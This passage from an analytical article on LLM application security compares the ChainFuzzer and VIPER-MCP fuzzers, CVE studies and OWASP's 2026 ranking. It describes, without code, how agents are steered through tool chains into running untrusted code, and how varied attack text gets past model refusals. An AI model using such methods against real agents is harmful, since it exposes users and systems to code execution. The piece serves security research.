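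Two earlier tools took a similar approach. LLMSmith (2024) searched frameworks such as LangChain for chains of function calls that end in running code, then tried prompts on applications built with them. AgentFuzz (USENIX Security 2025) fuzzed agents and used the result of each run to steer the next prompt closer to a sink.

Testing tools one at a time can miss a flaw that appears only when several are used together. *ChainFuzzer* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to find a patch for a bug. The agent searches the web, downloads a result, saves it as a file and runs it. Each step is reasonable for the task, but together they result in the agent running untrusted code from the web.

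ChainFuzzer works backwards from dangerous functions. It looks for tools whose arguments can reach one, then for other tools that could supply those arguments, either directly or through a file or database record. Next it needs a prompt that makes the agent call these tools in the right order, which is difficult because small changes in wording can lead the model to a different plan. ChainFuzzer runs a prompt, compares the agent's tool calls with the intended chain and repairs the prompt if they differ. With these repairs, it could get the agent to follow 95% of the chains, up from 27% without them.

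The last step is to put attack text into the chain. Models often refuse or weaken obviously malicious text, and only 18% of the plain versions worked, compared with 89% when ChainFuzzer varied their form. A model's refusal of one crude attack is therefore little evidence that the tool behind it is safe.

| | VIPER-MCP | ChainFuzzer |
|---|---|---|
| Published | May 2026 | March 2026 |
| What it searches | Single tools on MCP servers | Single tools and chains of tools in agents |
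| Programs tested | 39,884 repositories | 20 applications with 998 tools |
| Confirmed flaws | 106 | 365, of which 302 need several tools |
| Accuracy | No false alarms; 7.7% of flaws missed | 91.5% of a checked sample of candidate chains were correct |

The accuracy figures measure different things. ChainFuzzer's figure describes the chains it proposed before fuzzing, so it isn't a false-alarm rate for the 365 flaws. VIPER-MCP's perfect score follows largely from its design, since it reports a flaw only after triggering it. As a result, it can't distinguish a safe tool from one whose flaw it failed to trigger. It missed 7.7% of the known flaws, compared with 64% and 73% for the two older scanners in the comparison, which also had false-alarm rates of 25% to 43%. But researchers can calculate a miss rate only from flaws they already know about, so they can't use it to estimate how many remain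 in the 39,884 repositories.

VIPER-MCP confirmed about one flaw for every 376 repositories, while ChainFuzzer confirmed about 18 per application, with at least one in 19 of the 20 applications. Much of this gap probably comes from what the researchers chose to test and count. Wu and colleagues picked popular agents with an average of 50 tools each, whereas many MCP servers are small wrappers around one program. Sun and colleagues looked for only three types of flaw and excluded tools meant to run arbitrary commands, such as the one at the end of the patch example. Neither figure is a rate for software in general.

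Wu and colleagues report that their method finds about three flaws per million tokens. At Claude Opus 5.5's prices, without caching, each flaw would cost between $1.30 and $6.60 to find, depending on how many of the tokens were output. An attacker could afford the same search but would need the tools' source code, which is public for open-source agents but not for most companies' own applications.

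### Flaws in the public record

Sun and colleagues had received 67 CVE numbers for their 106 flaws when they published, so even a confirmed flaw may be missing from the CVE catalogue for a while. The catalogue is still one of the few sources for a count. For their 2025 study of the LLM supply chain (the software used to build and run applications on language models), Wang and colleagues collected 4,157 records from vulnerability databases, a bug-bounty site and security companies. After they removed duplicates, irrelevant entries and anything from before late 2022, when ChatGPT came out, 529 vulnerabilities in 77 open-source projects remained.

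The 24 that they traced to unvalidated model output make up 4.5% of the total:

| What the output led to | Vulnerabilities |
|---|---|
| Code or command injection | 11 |
| SQL injection | 5 |
| File manipulation | 4 |
| Cross-site scripting | 3 |
| Server-side request forgery | 1 |

The study uses "SQL injection" loosely, because its example is a LangChain component that let attackers inject commands into Neo4j, a database that uses its own query language rather than SQL.

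Uncontrolled resource consumption accounts for 23 vulnerabilities, almost the same number. These include unlimited memory allocation and slow regular expressions, which can make a program crash or stall. They are much more like the vLLM flaws described earlier than the kind that leads to a $50,000 bill.

The researchers classed 431 of the vulnerabilities in the sample (81.5%) as traditional, meaning they have little to do with how language models work. These include 121 that let attackers reach files outside the intended folder and 91 ordinary injection flaws. Whether a flaw was labelled "traditional" or "model output" depended on how the researchers read each report, but two of them labelled the entries independently and largely agreed.

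The sample also reflects where people look for flaws. Two thirds of the entries came from huntr, a bug-bounty site that pays people to report flaws. The researchers included only open-source projects with more than 1,000 stars on GitHub, so EchoLeak, which affected a Microsoft product, could not appear. A flaw in the furniture shop's own program could not appear either, because CVEs are mainly used to let other people know what to upgrade, and only the shop runs its chat box.

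A published fix protects a server only once its owner installs it. Wang and colleagues checked the software versions of 63,243 LLM services that anyone could reach over the internet against known vulnerabilities, and 45.6% had at least one that an attacker could exploit remotely. This figure covers vulnerabilities of every kind. Three popular programs (Ollama, Open WebUI and Dify) accounted for more than 90% of the affected services.

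### OWASP's 2026 ranking

For its 2026 list, OWASP gathered a much larger collection of 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms caused by AI. ReversingLabs, a software-security company, reports that the project built classifiers to read the records and that 6,639 had enough detail to sort. Votes by security practitioners had decided the earlier rankings. They still counted for three quarters of the 2026 result, and the incidents for one quarter, because OWASP thought a single year of imperfect data should not overrule hundreds of practitioners.

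Invicti gives the order in OWASP's document, and SC Media lists the risks in the same order:

| 2026 | Risk | 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Prompt injection | 1 |
| 2 | Sensitive information disclosure | 2 |
| 3 | Excessive agency | 6 |
| 4 | Supply chain | 3 |
| 5 | Data and model poisoning | 4 |
| 6 | Unbounded consumption | 10 |
| 7 | Misinformation | 9 |
| 8 | Hidden context exposure (formerly system prompt leakage) | 7 |
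| 9 | Vector and embedding weaknesses | 8 |
| 10 | Improper output handling | 5 |

Some coverage of the list gets details wrong. ReversingLabs swaps the positions of unbounded consumption and misinformation. Invicti says excessive agency rose the most, but it rose three places and unbounded consumption rose four.

The rankings by votes and by incidents differed most on two other risks. Practitioners ranked prompt injection first, but it would have missed the top ten on incidents alone. They ranked misinformation near the bottom, but it ranked near the top by incidents. OWASP attributes prompt injection's low incident count to a "defense effect", in which developers guard so heavily against a well-known risk that few successful attacks reach the public databases. That is plausible, but the count would also be low if attacks were rare.

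### What the ranks leave out

A rank compares one risk with nine others and doesn't measure its size. All five risks that ranked below improper output handling in 2025 now rank above it. Advait Patel, a cloud security engineer who created one of OWASP's tools, told ReversingLabs that the risk fell because "everything above it got more urgent", not because output handling had become safe. Invicti gives the same explanation. They may be right, but the ranking would look the same if output handling had become safer while the other risks stayed the same. One of the five, vector and embedding weaknesses (flaws in how applications store and search text by its meaning), fell one place and still overtook output handling.

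The same caution applies to the rise of unbounded consumption, where the incident data is probably weakest. Vulnerability databases record flaws in products, and there was no faulty version to list when someone copied the Brazilian tyre shop's key and ran up $7,500 in an hour. There was no CVE when Jenkins's agent wasted $1,000, either. A database of AI harms might include such cases, but only if the victims make them public, and a company has little reason to disclose that it lost $50,000 to a loop. The incident count could therefore be far too low for this risk, and the risk's new rank may owe more to what practitioners have seen on their own bills than to incident data.

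An "incident" may also be a flaw that has caused no known harm. Patel says the incident data shows what has caused real-world harm, but a vulnerability entry shows only that a flaw existed. The entry for OpenClaw's false approval screen, for example, lists no known exploitation. A separate public collection, *GenAI & Agentic AI Security Incidents*, defines incidents even more broadly, including research demonstrations, vulnerabilities that nobody has exploited, and every test in garak, NVIDIA's scanner for language models. Nothing indicates that OWASP counted scanner tests, but a total can depend heavily on how "incident" is defined.

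Incidents are also hard to sort because one incident can belong to several categories. EchoLeak, for example, involved prompt injection, improper output handling and sensitive information disclosure, so a classifier that gives each incident a single label would leave it out of the count for two of them. Wang and colleagues count their 24 vulnerabilities as failures to validate output, yet each label begins with "Prompt Injection Leads to". Under OWASP's categories, someone could file all 24 as either prompt injection or improper output handling. In a collection of thousands, the choice would make little difference to the total for prompt injection, but it could substantially change the total for a small category.

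OWASP acknowledges the overlap in its document. *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽* (Eric, 2026) describes a diagram from the document that sorts the risks into entry points, amplifiers and final effects. Improper output handling is one of four amplifiers, which make a successful injection more harmful, and dashed borders show that all four can belong to more than one group. This grouping is more useful to the shop's developer than the rank, because a chat box that puts replies on the page as raw HTML has a serious flaw whether OWASP lists it fifth or tenth.

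### Whether improper output handling is a new problem

Some security engineers doubt that improper output handling needed its own name. Auth0's *Trusting AI Output?* calls it "the new XSS" and argues that classic flaws such as SQL injection are back. On this view, a model is another way for untrusted text to reach a program, and developers have known for decades how to handle such text.

Much of the evidence supports this. The three kinds of flaw that VIPER-MCP looks for all had entries in the weakness catalogue long before anyone connected a language model to a shell, and the sanitisers it recognises are the usual ones. Microsoft filed EchoLeak under an old category. The maintainer of the AWS server fixed its flaw in the server, without changing the model.

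A common reply is that attacks on models have proved harder to stop than older kinds of attack. Steve Wilson, who founded OWASP's project on generative AI security, told ReversingLabs that prompt injection once seemed like SQL injection, a flaw developers could largely avoid with enough care, but that this view proved false. Jason Soroko of the security company Sectigo adds that each defence makes an attack less likely but doesn't rule it out.

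This is true, but it concerns the model's input. It doesn't show that the output needs new treatment, since correct encoding works wherever the text came from.

Some programs, such as `ask_database`, let the model write the whole command, so the developer has to rely on access control instead of separating values from commands. Both methods are old, but developers could once also rely on having written the queries themselves.

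The old methods of finding flaws also need changes. A scanner that follows text from a web form to a sink will miss the flaws in both `find_product` and `ask_database` unless someone configures it to treat the model's replies as untrusted. That is a small adjustment for `find_product`, but it helps much less with the 302 flaws that ChainFuzzer found across several tools, because the model selects at run time which tool receives the text next.
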